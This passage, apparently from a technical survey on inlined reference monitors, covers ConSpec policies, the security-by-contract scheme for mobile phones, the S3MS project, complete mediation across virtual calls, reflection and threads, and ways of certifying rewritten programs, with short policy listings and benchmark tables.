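    upload:     i -> i-1
download:       2 -> violation
```

Jones and Hamlen needed some knowledge of XNap's internal structure to write this policy, which they got from a brief look at the disassembled bytecode. They describe two ways to cheat the policy. A user can restart the program after every two downloads, which resets the counter. The policy also counts an upload as soon as it joins the queue, so a user can cancel it and keep the credit. They report no rewriting time or overhead for XNap.

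### ConSpec: scope, state and clauses

ConSpec addresses the restart problem directly. Each policy begins with a scope, which determines how long the monitor remembers events and whose events it counts:

| Scope | What a limit of five text messages would mean |
|---|---|
| Object | Five for each object of a given class |
| Session | Five in each run of an application |
| Multisession | Five across all runs of one application |
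| Global | Five across all applications on the device |

The state variables and a list of clauses follow the scope. Each clause names a method and specifies whether the clause's code runs `BEFORE` the call, `AFTER` a normal return, or on an `EXCEPTIONAL` return, when the method throws an exception. The clause contains guards, which are conditions, each paired with an update to the state. The monitor checks the guards from top to bottom and performs the update for the first one that is true. If none is true and the clause has no `ELSE` branch, the event violates the policy.

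The file-and-message policy is short in ConSpec:

```
SCOPE Session
SECURITY STATE
    bool hasRead = false;

BEFORE java.io.FileInputStream.read()
PERFORM
    true -> { hasRead = true; }

BEFORE java.net.SocketOutputStream.write(int b)
PERFORM
    !hasRead -> { skip; }
```

Once `hasRead` is true, the only guard for a send is false, so the monitor stops the program if it tries to send. If the first clause used `AFTER`, a read that failed with an exception would not set `hasRead`.

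A policy sometimes needs both a `BEFORE` and an `AFTER` clause for one method. In *Security by Contract on the .NET Platform*, Desmet, Joosen and colleagues give a policy that limits a program to 1,000 bytes of network traffic. The `BEFORE` clause checks that the bytes already sent plus the length of the new message do not exceed 1,000. A program that has sent 950 bytes and tries to send 55 more fails this check. The `AFTER` clause adds the send method's return value, which is the number of bytes actually sent, to the total.

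### What ConSpec leaves out

ConSpec is similar to PSLang but more restricted. Its state variables can hold only booleans, integers and strings, and the policy file sets a maximum for the integers and the length of the strings. Guards cannot have side effects, and updates cannot contain loops. A policy can test whether two strings are equal or whether one begins with the other, but it cannot search a string for a pattern. Each method can have only one clause of each kind, so the policy never specifies two different responses to the same event.

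These limits give every policy a finite number of states and an exact meaning as an automaton. Aktug and Naliuka explain that with a language as powerful as PSLang, no algorithm could always decide whether one policy permits everything that another does. They also list which features each task could support:

| Feature | Proof before the program runs | Comparing two policies | Monitoring |
|---|---|---|---|
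| Booleans | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Integers and strings with a maximum | No | Yes | Yes |
| Memory across runs or applications | No | Yes | Yes |
| Lists, unlimited values and loops | No | No | Yes |

A monitor could handle everything in the table, so the restrictions exist for the other two tasks. They rule out some useful policies. For example, a policy that lets a program delete only the files it has created needs a list of names, and ConSpec has no lists. A policy author could declare ten string variables to store the names, but the policy could then track only ten files.

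### Security-by-contract

Aktug and Naliuka designed ConSpec for security-by-contract, a scheme for phones that download applications from unknown developers. Phones of the time relied on digital signatures, which show who signed an application but not what it does. Desmet and colleagues mention malware that a commercial certification company had signed. In *Security-by-Contract*, Massacci, Naliuka and Siahaan (2007) proposed that a signature should bind an application to a contract describing everything the application might do that matters for security.

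The process has these steps:

1. The developer writes a contract and obtains evidence that the application obeys it. A trusted company can inspect the code and sign it together with the contract, or the developer can supply a formal proof that the phone is able to check.
2. The phone checks the evidence.
3. The phone compares the contract with the user's policy. If every sequence of actions that the contract allows is one that the policy allows, the two match.
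4. If they match, the application runs without a monitor. If they don't, or if the application has no trustworthy contract, the phone inlines a monitor for the user's policy.

Comparing the contract with the policy is a standard problem in automata theory. If L(C) is the set of sequences that the contract allows and L(P) is the set that the policy allows, the phone must check that L(C) ⊆ L(P). It searches for a counterexample, a sequence that the contract allows and the policy forbids.

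Aktug and Naliuka illustrate this with a user, Alice, whose policy allows each application at most five text messages a day. An application called Weather sends one message every morning to request a forecast, and its contract allows one message a day. HappyBirthday sends a message to each of Alice's contacts who has a birthday. Its developers can't know how many that will be, so their contract sets no number. The phone follows each contract and the policy together, one message at a time:

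| Message that day | Weather's contract | HappyBirthday's contract | Alice's policy |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Allows it | Allows it | Allows it |
| 2 | Forbids it, so the search ends with a match | Allows it | Allows it |
| 3 to 5 | – | Allows them | Allows them |
| 6 | – | Allows it | Forbids it, so the two do not match |

Weather runs unmodified, while HappyBirthday runs with an inlined monitor that stops it if it tries to send a sixth message. The mismatch means only that HappyBirthday's contract doesn't rule out a violation. If Alice never has more than five contacts with the same birthday, the monitor never intervenes.

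The scopes matter as well. A contract that allows one message per run would not match Alice's policy, because the application could run six times in a day.

### How long matching takes

Real policies often depend on values that can't be listed in advance. A rule that allows only secure connections would need a separate transition for every web address that starts with `https://`. Massacci and Siahaan (2009), in *Inclusion Matching Implementation of Automata Modulo Theory (AMT)*, instead put a condition on the transition, such as "the address starts with `https://`". Their program searches through pairs of states, one from the contract and one from the policy. For each pair of transitions, it uses a solver to check whether one event could satisfy both conditions.

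They tested it on a desktop computer and on an HTC phone with a 400 MHz processor and 64 MB of memory. The table shows three of their nine tests, with average times in seconds.

| Contract | Policy | Result | Desktop | Phone |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No connections after opening personal data | Only secure connections after opening personal data | Match | 4.7 | 4.1 |
| Ordinary web connections | Secure web connections | No match | 2.8 | 3.8 |
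| No text messages | At most 100 text messages | Match | 9.3 | 11.3 |

A wait of about four seconds is acceptable when a user installs an application. The phone was hardly slower than a desktop with more than eight times the clock speed, so much of the time may be fixed overhead, such as starting the solver, though one version of the program runs on Java and the other on .NET. The text-message test took longer because its policy has 102 states, while the others have two or three. Massacci and Siahaan call this test artificial, but Alice's policy is of the same kind, and a limit in the thousands could make the wait much longer.

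### What the S3MS project built

The European Union project S3MS (Security of Software and Services for Mobile Systems) developed security-by-contract for Windows Mobile phones, along with a version for Java. According to *Nomadic devices, the freedom to compute* (2008), the project showed a prototype to companies in December 2007, and one of its partners, France Télécom, was completing a report on commercial uses.

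When an application arrives, the phone tries its methods of checking in turn. It can look for a signature that certifies compliance with a particular policy, or it can match the contract. Inlining comes last because it works without a contract but slows the application and might introduce subtle bugs. Desmet, Joosen and colleagues (2009), in *The S3MS.NET Run Time Monitor*, show what the rewriter does to a call that sends a text message. In simplified form, the result is:

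```
PDP.BeforeSendSMS(message);      // throws an exception to refuse the call
try {
    message.SendSMS();           // the original call
    PDP.AfterSendSMS(message);
} catch (Exception e) {
    PDP.ExceptionSendSMS(message, e);
    throw;                       // pass the exception on to the program
}
```

The three added calls correspond to ConSpec's three kinds of clause. `PDP` stands for policy decision point, a separate library that the project's compiler generates from the policy. The rewriter therefore inlines only the calls to the monitor, while the policy's logic and state stay outside the application.

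A developer can also inline a monitor before distributing the application, so the phone doesn't have to do it and the developer can test the modified version. A certifier can then check part of a policy by inspection and leave the rest to the monitor. For example, if a policy forbids network access and limits writing to 1,000 bytes, the certifier can easily see that an application has no network code, and the monitor only has to count the bytes.

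The project tried the monitor on a two-player chess game played by text message and on a multiplayer role-playing game. Desmet and colleagues report no noticeable effect on the performance of either game, but give no figures. Students at the Catholic University of Leuven also used the tool to enforce policies on an email program.

Desmet and colleagues acknowledge that policies are hard to write. To limit network traffic, a policy writer must find every method that could cause it and predict how many bytes each will use. The 1,000-byte policy above covers only one method for sending data, but a program can also cause traffic by looking up a web address or following a redirect. The researchers expected phone operators and large companies to write most policies, since few phone users would have the skills.

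### Imperative and declarative languages compared

Imperative languages can express more responses than declarative ones. A ConSpec policy by Aktug and Naliuka requires a program that has opened an existing file to get the user's approval before it makes a connection. The policy can check that the program called a method named `AskConnect` and that the answer was "Yes". It can't display the question itself, so an application that doesn't call `AskConnect` loses its network access after it opens an existing file. A Polymer policy can insert the dialog box into any program.

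Hamlen and Jones estimate that SPoX and ConSpec are about equally expressive, except that ConSpec can only name method calls as events. But ConSpec's scopes can cover several runs and applications, while SPoX, as used on XNap, could not keep state across restarts.

Declarative policies are much easier to analyse. A phone can compare two ConSpec policies in seconds, but nobody can reliably compare policies written in arbitrary Java code. Aktug and Naliuka also argue that nobody can prove the inlining of PSLang or Polymer policies correct, because neither language has a formal semantics. They overlook Polymer's formal model, although that model leaves out the rewriter.

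Hamlen and Jones suggest combining some of the benefits of both styles by letting policy authors supply recovery code separately from the policy, for example to undo an operation after a violation. A verifier would treat this code as untrusted and reject it if it broke the policy.

Declarative policies are not always shorter than imperative ones. The file-and-message policy is about the same length in PSLang and ConSpec. The XNap policy would probably be shorter in PSLang, where one variable and an `if` statement could replace the ranges of edges. Columba's four-line rule is short because the long list of methods is in a library, which an imperative language could also use.

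Removing advice prevents some errors, such as a policy whose own code performs a forbidden action. Errors in the vocabulary remain possible in either style, and declarative policies can also contain logic errors. In the printed XNap policy, the range for downloads runs up to 2, so a download in state 2 matches two edges. One leads to a violation, as Jones and Hamlen intended, and the other leads to state 3. Under the usual rule for nondeterministic automata, the policy would allow the download. The range should stop at 1. A tool could detect this overlap automatically, and ConSpec avoids the ambiguity by always using the first true guard.

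## Complete mediation: dynamic dispatch, reflection, native code and threads

Even if a policy lists the right methods and has correct logic, the rewriter still has to find every call to those methods. This is difficult because a call instruction doesn't always name the method that will run, and a program can load new code after the rewriter has finished. In a multithreaded program, another thread can also act between a check and the call it guards.

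### Caller-side and callee-side checks

A rewriter can put its checks around each call in the target (caller-side) or inside the body of the called method (callee-side). The S3MS project's .NET monitor uses caller-side checks, while Polymer uses callee-side ones.

| | Caller-side | Callee-side |
|---|---|---|
| Code that the rewriter edits | The target | Usually the system libraries |
| Calls that the monitor checks | Those in the target | All calls, including those that the libraries make themselves |
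| Main difficulty | Recognising every relevant call | Distinguishing the target's calls from the libraries' own |

Vanoverberghe and Piessens, who designed a caller-side rewriter for S3MS, acknowledge that complete mediation is much easier to achieve with callee-side checks. The target has to run a method's body no matter how it calls the method. They chose caller-side checks partly because a rewriter can't always modify the system libraries. A phone may store them in read-only memory, for example.

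Caller-side checks also let a policy forbid an application to open files but still allow it to call a library's logging method, which writes to a file. The monitor ignores the file operation because it happens inside the library. However, a caller-side policy has to list more methods. To limit network traffic, it must cover every library method that leads to a low-level method that sends data, whereas a callee-side monitor can check just the low-level methods.

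### Virtual calls

When a program calls a virtual method, the runtime chooses which version to run based on the object's actual class. Suppose a library has a class `Stream` with a `write` method, and a subclass `SocketStream` that overrides it. A policy restricts `SocketStream.write`.

If a variable has the type `Stream`, a call through it names `Stream.write`, even when the object is a `SocketStream`. A rewriter that looks only for `SocketStream.write` would miss this call. Vanoverberghe and Piessens therefore require that if a policy covers a method, it also covers every method that this one overrides. The policy doesn't have to restrict the added methods, but the rewriter must insert code at every call to `Stream.write`, including calls that only write to memory.

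Subclasses defined in the application cause a different problem. If the application defines `MyStream` as a subclass of `SocketStream` without its own `write`, a call to `MyStream.write` runs the restricted library method. The policy's author usually doesn't know that `MyStream` exists, so the policy can't list it. The remedy is to require application classes to redefine every security-relevant method they would otherwise inherit. The redefined `write` can call `SocketStream.write` with an instruction that the rewriter recognises. A tool could add these redefinitions automatically.

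The rewriter also can't determine in advance which rule applies to a call that names `Stream.write`. It inserts a call to a dispatcher, which tests the object's class at run time:

```
BeforeWrite(stream):
    if stream is a SocketStream:      apply the rule for SocketStream.write
    else if stream is a FileStream:   apply the rule for FileStream.write
    else:                             do nothing
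```

### Delegates

A .NET delegate is an object that holds a set of methods, and calling the delegate runs all of them. The application can add methods to the set at run time, so the instruction that calls a delegate doesn't show which methods will run.

When the application creates a delegate for a security-relevant method, the rewriter substitutes a wrapper that it adds to the application. The wrapper's checks then run on every call to the delegate.

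This remedy works only if the system libraries never give the application a delegate that already contains a security-relevant method. Vanoverberghe and Piessens found that the libraries met this condition for the methods they considered. Extending a policy to new methods or changing the libraries would require a new check.

### What Vanoverberghe and Piessens prove

The proof uses a simplified model of .NET and establishes complete mediation, transparency and a third property, sound mediation, which means that the monitor never records a call that didn't take place. The argument for complete mediation has three steps:

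1. The program can enter a block of inserted code only at its first instruction, because the rewriter adjusts every jump in the original code.
2. The rewriter has processed every call instruction that can run a security-relevant method.
3. Each inserted block notifies the monitor before the method starts and again after it returns or throws an exception.

The second step is trivial for non-virtual methods, but virtual calls and delegates break it. Vanoverberghe and Piessens prove the non-virtual case in detail and argue more informally that their remedies restore the step. Their model has one thread and no interfaces, and it assumes that security-relevant methods always finish and never call back into the application.

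The full .NET system required further work. For example, a program can't enter a try block while it has values on its evaluation stack, so the rewriter first has to save them in local variables.

### Reflection, class loading and native code

When a Java program calls a method through reflection, the call instruction names the reflection library's `Method.invoke`, regardless of which method will run. *Provably correct inline monitoring for multithreaded Java-like programs* (Dam, Jacobs and colleagues, 2010) excludes reflection from its guarantee because its rewriter has to recognise library calls. Checks placed inside the called method still run under reflection, but the monitor must also prevent the program from using reflection to change the monitor's variables.

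Class loading and native code raise related problems, and the designer of a monitor has three choices for each feature:

| Feature | Forbid it | Wrap it | Rewrite code as it is loaded |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reflection | Simple, but breaks programs that need it | Check the requested method inside a wrapper for `Method.invoke` | Does not help alone, because the program chooses the method later |
| Class loading | Simple, but rules out plug-ins | Load only classes that a trusted party has approved | Insert the usual checks before each new class runs |
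| Native code | Possible only for code that the target supplies | Check the calls that enter it | Not possible for a bytecode rewriter |

SASI forbade both reflection and class loading. *Taming reflection* provides some evidence that a complete ban is often unnecessary. Its tool, TamiFlex, records a program's reflective calls in sample runs so that static analysis can account for them, then inserts run-time checks that warn about calls missing from the record. On DaCapo, a standard set of Java benchmarks, *Taming reflection* reports no warnings and an overhead usually below 10%. A security monitor could use a similar record as a list of permitted calls. It would have to block any other call rather than just warn about it, so an incomplete record could stop a legitimate program.

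Several systems rewrite classes at load time. Welch and Stroud developed Kava, a version of Java that inserts hooks into each class as the program loads it, and Polymer does the same with a custom class loader. Programs can still use plug-ins, but the rewriter must be present throughout the run and makes loading slower. It must also process classes loaded by the program's own class loaders.

Load-time rewriting matters even if a policy's author has searched the whole program for relevant calls. KTH's *Inlined Reference Monitors for Multithreaded Java* includes a case study of JPicEdt, a drawing program with about 68,000 lines of code. The policy requires the program to call Swing, Java's graphical interface library, from one particular thread. It lists only the Swing methods that JPicEdt mentions. That list was enough to reveal that the program broke the rule at start-up, but a plug-in could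 call Swing methods that aren't on it.

Tilevich and Smaragdakis (2006) point out that a bytecode rewriter can't insert checks into native code, and that such code can invalidate the rewriter's assumptions about the rest of the program. Every Java program depends on some native code, because even `Object`, the class all others inherit from, uses it. A monitor therefore has to trust the native code in the system libraries and check the calls that lead to it. If the target program includes its own native code, as some phone apps do, the monitor must refuse it or confine it with software fault isolation or a separate process. Confinement brings back overhead that inlining in Java had avoided.

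### When another thread acts after the check

The file-and-message policy can fail in a program with two threads even if the rewriter has found every call:

| Step | Thread 1 | Thread 2 | `hasRead` |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | – | Checks `hasRead` before a send and passes | false |
| 2 | Sets `hasRead` before a read | – | true |
| 3 | Reads the file | – | true |
| 4 | – | Sends the message | true |

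If thread 1 reads the file into the array that thread 2 is about to send, the message will contain the file.

Programs usually protect shared data with a lock, which only one thread can hold at a time. Dam and colleagues compare two ways of using one. In weak synchronization, which PoET used, the monitor holds the lock while it checks and updates its state, then releases it before the call begins. This keeps the monitor's variables consistent, but the sequence in the table can still occur. In strong synchronization, the monitor holds the lock until the call returns. Thread 1 then can't start its read until thread 2 has finished sending, so the policy holds.

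Strong synchronization can deadlock a correct program. Suppose a library method makes each of two threads wait until the other has called it. The first thread calls the method and waits while holding the monitor's lock. The second thread needs the lock before it can make its call, so neither can continue. Even without a deadlock, a slow network operation would delay every other security-relevant call in the program.

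Locks can also remove behaviour that the policy allows. Java lets compilers and processors reorder a thread's accesses to shared variables if the program doesn't synchronise them. In an example by Dam and colleagues, thread 1 writes to one variable, makes a security-relevant call and writes to another variable. Thread 2 makes an extra call only if it finds the second write but not the first. Reordering makes the extra call possible in the original program, but the inserted locks prevent that call.

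Dam and colleagues therefore replace transparency with a weaker property, strong conservativity. It requires every complete run of the rewritten program to match either a complete run of the original or the part of such a run that comes before a violation. They prove that an inliner with strong synchronization has this property, provided that the security-relevant methods never block and the virtual machine raises no internal errors. They also assume that the method named in a call instruction is the one that will run. *Provably Correct Runtime Monitoring*, an earlier paper by Aktug, Dam and Gurov, handles inheritance for single-threaded programs.

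The inliner worked on four phone applications, each with two to four security-relevant calls. Rewriting took 0.48 to 1.80 seconds on a laptop-class processor and made the programs 0.2% to 1.1% larger. One application, the game Snake, had a policy very similar to the file-and-message policy. It stopped the game from sending data over the network after reading from the phone's memory.

To measure how much time a check adds, Dam and colleagues called an empty method a million times on a Sony Ericsson phone. The loop took 407 milliseconds before rewriting and 1,358 afterwards, so each checked call took about 951 nanoseconds longer, which is negligible next to a network operation. But the test didn't measure the time threads spend waiting for one another, which could be the main delay from strong synchronization.

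### Race-free policies

*Security Monitor Inlining for Multithreaded Java* (Dam, Jacobs and colleagues, 2009) shows that no inliner for multithreaded Java can be both secure and transparent for every policy. *Security monitor inlining and certification for multithreaded Java* (Dam, Jacobs and colleagues, 2014) shows that inlining can be both secure and transparent only for policies called race-free, and gives an inliner that is secure, transparent and conservative for all such policies.

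The 2010 paper describes a race-free policy as "insensitive to the sequencing of concurrent actions". Inserted code runs just before a call or just after a return, so other threads may act between a check and the start of the call. Roughly, a policy is race-free if a call that passes its check remains permissible whatever other threads do in that gap.

The file-and-message policy is not race-free, because a read in another thread can make a send impermissible after it has passed its check. A policy from KTH's case studies meets the condition. It applies to a model of a shop's cash desk and requires that the number of finished sales never exceed the number started:

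```
AFTER newSaleStarted()
PERFORM
    true -> { salesInProgress = salesInProgress + 1; }

BEFORE saleFinished()
PERFORM
    salesInProgress > 0 -> { salesInProgress = salesInProgress - 1; }
```

The monitor counts a sale only after the start method returns, and it subtracts one before the finish method begins. A thread that passes the check has therefore already reserved one of the open sales. Other threads may start sales or reserve different ones before the finish method begins, but they can't undo this reservation, so a short lock around each update to the count is enough.

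Where a policy updates its state can determine whether it is race-free. The contract for the S3MS chess game checks the text-message limit before each message but counts the message afterwards. With weak synchronization, two threads could both pass the check when only one message remained. Counting each message in the `BEFORE` clause would prevent this, but messages that failed to send would also count unless another clause corrected the total.

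Not every policy can be rewritten this way. A reservation can't help with the file-and-message policy, because a send has to stop other threads from reading until it begins. The monitor could make the reading thread wait, much as Luo and Rosu (2013) do to ensure that one thread authorises a user before another fetches the user's data. But waiting, like a lock, restricts how the threads can run.

The 2014 result guarantees transparency for race-free policies, but the 2010 example shows that inserted locks can remove permitted behaviour from badly synchronised programs. The 2014 result presumably uses a model of Java that leaves out this kind of reordering.

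### Guarantees that survive a gap in coverage

The damage from an unchecked call depends on whether the policy uses history. The policy for another S3MS application, a traffic reporter, allows connections only to addresses that begin with `http://local.yahooapis.com`. If the monitor misses one connection, that connection may break the policy, but the checks on the others still work. If the file-and-message monitor misses one read, `hasRead` stays false and every later send passes its check. A missed event can also stop a legitimate program. The cash-desk monitor would block the end of a sale if it had missed the start.

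| Left uncovered | What still holds | What can fail |
|---|---|---|
| Some virtual, delegate or reflective calls | Policies that judge each call separately, at the calls that the rewriter recognised | Policies on the missed calls, and later decisions that depend on them |
| Classes loaded during the run | The same, for calls in the original code | Every caller-side check in the new code |
| Native code supplied by the target | Nothing, unless another mechanism confines the code | All checks, because the code can use resources directly and overwrite the monitor's state |
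| Other threads, with weak synchronization | Race-free policies | Policies that depend on the order of concurrent calls |
| Other threads, with strong synchronization | Security | Transparency, speed and freedom from deadlock |

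## Checking the rewritten program instead of trusting the rewriter

A rewriter can leave a call unchecked because of a difficult language feature or an ordinary programming error. Every policy depends on the rewriter, so one such error can defeat a correct policy. Some rewriters are too large to inspect. SASI needed only a few thousand lines, but the S3MS project's inliner has over 900,000 lines of Java, including the underlying AspectJ system, according to *Aspect-Oriented Runtime Monitor Certification* (Hamlen, Jones and Sridhar, 2012).

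Rewriters also change often. In *Flexible In-lined Reference Monitor Certification*, Sridhar and Hamlen give the example of web advertising, where developers revise their checks as new attacks appear. A proof that one version of a rewriter is correct can take a long time to produce and soon becomes obsolete.

Certification removes the rewriter from the trusted computing base. An untrusted rewriter produces the modified program, usually with some evidence that it obeys the policy, and a small trusted checker accepts or rejects that program. Java already treats compilers this way, since the virtual machine checks their output.

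### Why checking can be simpler than rewriting

No algorithm can decide for every program whether it obeys a policy such as the file-and-message rule. A certifier avoids this problem because it only has to recognise the kind of program that a cooperative rewriter produces. If a call is hard to prove safe, the rewriter can put a run-time test before it. The certifier then has to confirm that the test is sufficient and that no path to the call bypasses it. It will reject some safe programs, but this does little harm if the rewriter can always produce a version that the certifier accepts.

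Certification also makes optimisation less risky. Erlingsson and Schneider left unnecessary checks in SASI's output partly because an optimiser would have enlarged the trusted computing base. With a certifier, the optimiser can remain untrusted, because the certifier rejects the program if the optimiser deletes a check that the policy needs.

### Mobile: security state in the types

Hamlen's *Security Policy Enforcement by Automated Program-Rewriting* (2006) presented Mobile, a type system for .NET bytecode. Mobile's types record an object's class, as ordinary types do, and also the security-relevant operations that the program has performed on the object. One of Hamlen's example policies requires a program to open an object that fetches web pages, read from it one to three times and close it, after which the program may repeat the sequence.

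The checker has to know when two variables refer to the same object. In this sketch, the comments show what it records after each line:

```
x.Open();       // x is object A, and A is open
y = x;          // x and y are both object A, and A is open
x.Close();      // A is closed
y.GetPage();    // rejected, because A is closed
```

If the checker kept a separate record for each variable, it would still treat `y` as open at the last line.

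This method fails when a program stores many objects in a list, because the checker can't determine which one the program will take out later. Mobile therefore lets the rewriter pack an object together with a number that represents the object's current state. The program must unpack the object before using it. When it does, inserted code tests the number, and the checker uses the result to determine which operations are safe.

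Hamlen's type checker is about 2,000 lines of OCaml, not counting libraries, and the rewriter is about 3,500. About half the checker repeats work that .NET's own verifier does, so he estimates that adding it to an existing .NET system would require about 1,000 lines of new trusted code. Checking time can grow exponentially with the size of the policy, but only quadratically with the size of the program. The user supplies the policy, so a malicious developer can't cause the exponential growth.

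Hamlen tested Mobile on the SciMark benchmarks, with a policy that limits calls to certain libraries, and on a small web server, with a policy that limits the connections each network socket accepts. The web server kept 99.97% of its original throughput. SciMark took 17% longer overall, and one benchmark took almost twice as long because the rewriter had wrapped a frequent call in another method.

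Hamlen then optimised the rewritten SciMark by hand, moving some checks out of loops while ensuring that the program still passed the type checker. This cut the overhead from 17% to 2.7%. Checks written by hand without regard to certification added 1.4%, so most of the original overhead came from the simple rewriter, not from the need to satisfy the checker.

Mobile's prototype works best for policies about individual objects. The file-and-message policy connects a read on one object with a send on another, and Hamlen left support for such program-wide events to future work.

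### Proof-carrying code for ConSpec monitors

In proof-carrying code, the developer supplies a program with a proof that it is safe, and the recipient checks the proof. *A Proof Carrying Code Framework for Inlined Reference Monitors in Java Bytecode* (Dam and Lundblad, 2018) applies this to ConSpec contracts. The developer inlines the monitor and generates the proof, so the phone needs only a proof checker.

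The developer's proof has to show that two monitors agree whenever the program makes or returns from a call. One is the real monitor in the program, which nobody trusts yet. The other is a "ghost" monitor, which the phone creates from the contract and adds to the program as annotations. The ghost monitor never runs, but it records for the proof which state the contract's automaton would be in at each point.

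Consider a contract that allows five text messages in each run. The program's monitor counts them in `sent`, and the ghost monitor counts them in `g`. The lines in braces are assertions, which must be true whenever the program reaches that point:

```
{ sent == g }
if (!(sent < 5)) exit();               // the check
{ sent == g  and  sent < 5 }
sent = sent + 1;                       // the state update
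{ sent == g + 1  and  g < 5 }
[ if g < 5: g = g + 1, else g = ERROR ]   // ghost update
{ sent == g }
sendSMS();                             // the guarded call
{ sent == g }
```

The program passes the check only if `sent` is below 5, which justifies the second assertion. The update makes `sent` one greater than `g`, and the ghost update makes them equal again. The last assertion before the call also rules out a violation, because `ERROR` is a special value that no Java variable can hold. If `sent` equals `g`, the automaton has not reached its error state.

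If a faulty rewriter omitted the state update, `sent` would be one less than `g` before the call, and the phone would reject the program. If the rewriter omitted the check, `g` might be `ERROR`, and the phone would reject that program too.

Formally, let A(L) be the assertion before instruction L, and let wp(L) be the weakest condition that guarantees that the assertions after L will hold. The checker verifies

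A(L) ⇒ wp(L)

for every instruction. It also verifies that the first assertion in each method follows from the condition that holds when the method starts. If every such step is valid, then by induction every assertion holds throughout the run.

Most instructions need almost no analysis. Dam and Lundblad store the monitor's state in a static field of a class that the program cannot extend, and in Java only one kind of instruction can change such a field. The checker confirms that the original code never uses that instruction on this field, so it can assume that the original code preserves `sent == g` and analyse only the inserted blocks. The developer must keep each block in one piece and prevent jumps into or out of it where the two monitors disagree.

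Dam and Lundblad's checker accepts any inserted code with a valid proof, so a developer can optimise the code at one call for speed and at another for size. Sridhar and Hamlen object that an earlier ConSpec verifier, which looked for prescribed code at each call, had to repeat much of the rewriter's work. That objection is weaker against Dam and Lundblad's checker because it doesn't prescribe the code.

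Dam and Lundblad tested the system on the traffic reporter and the Snake game from the S3MS project. They rewrote the programs and generated the proofs on a laptop-class processor, and checked the proofs on a Sony Ericsson phone. The table compares these tests with Hamlen's, which ran on desktop processors.

| Method and program | Original size | Monitor code added | Evidence added | Time to rewrite and produce evidence | Time to check |
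|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Mobile, SciMark | 32 KB | 725 bytes | 3,477 bytes | 0.43 s | 0.50 s |
| Mobile, web server | 20 KB | 83 bytes | 117 bytes | 0.12 s | 0.09 s |
| Proof-carrying code, traffic reporter | 428 KB | 4.8 KB | 20.6 KB | 14.8 s | 0.098 s |
| Proof-carrying code, Snake | 43.7 KB | 1.1 KB | 2.6 KB | 9.4 s | 0.117 s |

The phone checked each proof in about a tenth of a second, a delay that a user would hardly notice when starting an application. Rewriting each program and generating its proof had taken between 9 and 15 seconds on a much faster computer. The proofs are larger than the monitors they describe, but they added only about 5% to the size of the traffic reporter and 6% to Snake. These two programs contain six security-relevant calls between them, so the tests are weak evidence about programs with thousands. Dam and Lundblad call their checker simple but don't give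 its size.

### Model checking the rewritten code

Model checking needs less evidence from the rewriter, because the verifier computes which states the program can reach. *Model-Checking In-Lined Reference Monitors* (Sridhar and Hamlen, 2010) describes a verifier for ActionScript bytecode, which Flash animations and web advertisements used. The test policy prohibited an advertisement from redirecting the user's browser to another site.

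The verifier explores every path through the program, using approximations instead of exact values because it cannot try every possible input. At each point it tracks the states that the policy's automaton might be in, and it rejects the program if any path might lead to a violation. The approximations must cover every value that could occur, so the verifier sometimes rejects a program that would never break the policy.

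The monitor's variable and the automaton don't change at the same moment, because a monitor may update its variable just before a call or only after several calls. The 2010 verifier therefore records which events have occurred since the last update, up to a fixed limit. A higher limit lets rewriters update the variable less often but gives the verifier more cases to examine. A limit of one event was enough for Sridhar and Hamlen's implementation.

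Hamlen and colleagues extended the method to Java and SPoX in a verifier called Cheko. One of their examples allows a program to send ten emails. In simplified form, the rewriter inserts three lines before the send:

```
if (s >= 0 && s <= 9) temp = s + 1;
if (s == 10) exit();
s = temp;
Mail.send();
```

At the start, `s` and `temp` both equal the automaton's state, which the verifier represents as *A*. If `s` is between 0 and 9, the inserted code increases it by one, and the send then increases *A* by one, so the two are equal again. The send would violate the policy only if *A* were 10. But then `s` would also have been 10 at the second line, and the program would have stopped there, before the send. The verifier finds this contradiction and accepts the code. Without the second line there would be no contradiction, so the verifier would reject the program.

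The number of cases can grow quickly. If Cheko is tracking *n* cases and an event might match *m* policy rules, it may have to consider *n*(*m* + 1) cases afterwards. The SPoX rewriter therefore marks the regions where `s` and *A* may differ. Outside these regions, Cheko only has to confirm that they stay equal. Cheko does not assume the marks are correct, so wrong ones can slow it down or make it reject a safe program, but they can't make it accept an unsafe one.

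Hamlen and colleagues report that Cheko was practical for a variety of real Java applications and policies. It also checks more than a verifier that only looks for prescribed advice. SPoX policies contain no advice, so Cheko checks whether the inserted code achieves the policy's goal. Dam and Lundblad note the drawback that the recipient must do the whole analysis, whereas their system moves most of that work to the developer, who does it in advance.

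### Proving that legitimate programs still work

These certifiers prove compliance with the policy but not transparency. A rewriter could replace every program with one that exits immediately, and the result would comply with any policy that allows a program to do nothing.

Less extreme errors can also pass. If the rewriter in the text-message example used a limit of 3 instead of 5, all the assertions would still be true, because a count below 3 is also below 5. But the program would stop before sending a fourth message, which the contract allows. To exclude this error, a proof would also have to show that the monitor stops the program only when the automaton rejects the next action.

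Mobile's prototype has a fault of this kind. If two threads use the same package at once, the first unpacks the object and the second finds the package empty. The second thread receives an exception and terminates, even if the original program obeyed the policy. The type checker accepts the rewritten program because the program never breaks the policy.

Certifying transparency requires the original program as well as the rewritten one. Writing *e* for the original and *e′* for the rewritten version, the certifier must show that

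if *e* obeys the policy, then *e′* ≈ *e*

where ≈ means that the two programs behave in the same way. This relation is hard to define. It should ignore the monitor's own variables but detect changed results and new deadlocks. Comparing inputs with outputs works for simple programs, but many applications interact continually with users and other systems. A very strict definition would reject most monitors that keep a history, because they inevitably change the program in some way.

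Sridhar and Hamlen credit Chudnov and Naumann with the first formal proof of transparency for a real inlined monitor, which enforces information-flow policies. That proof and the one by Dam and colleagues for race-free policies both cover the rewriting algorithm in general. Neither provides a certificate for each rewritten program, so an error in the rewriter's implementation could still break a legitimate program undetected. In 2011, Sridhar and Hamlen listed automatic certification of transparency as an open problem.

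### What still has to be correct

This approach still requires trust in the checker and the libraries it uses to read programs and process policies. Dam and Lundblad formalised their soundness proof in Coq, a program that checks mathematical proofs. This gives good grounds to trust the method, but their checker could still contain a programming error.

The virtual machine also remains trusted, because all three methods rely on type safety to protect the monitor's state. In Mobile, the short library that packs and unpacks objects is trusted too.

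Certification can't detect a mistake in the policy. Hamlen calls his own policy notation very difficult for people to read and warns that a notation prone to human error can be a significant weakness. Certification also can't detect a call that the policy fails to map to an event. If the file-and-message policy omits reads through `FileChannel`, a program can read a secret file that way, send it and still have a valid certificate. Dam and Lundblad's proof treats each library method as a single step, without examining the code inside it, and excludes reflection.

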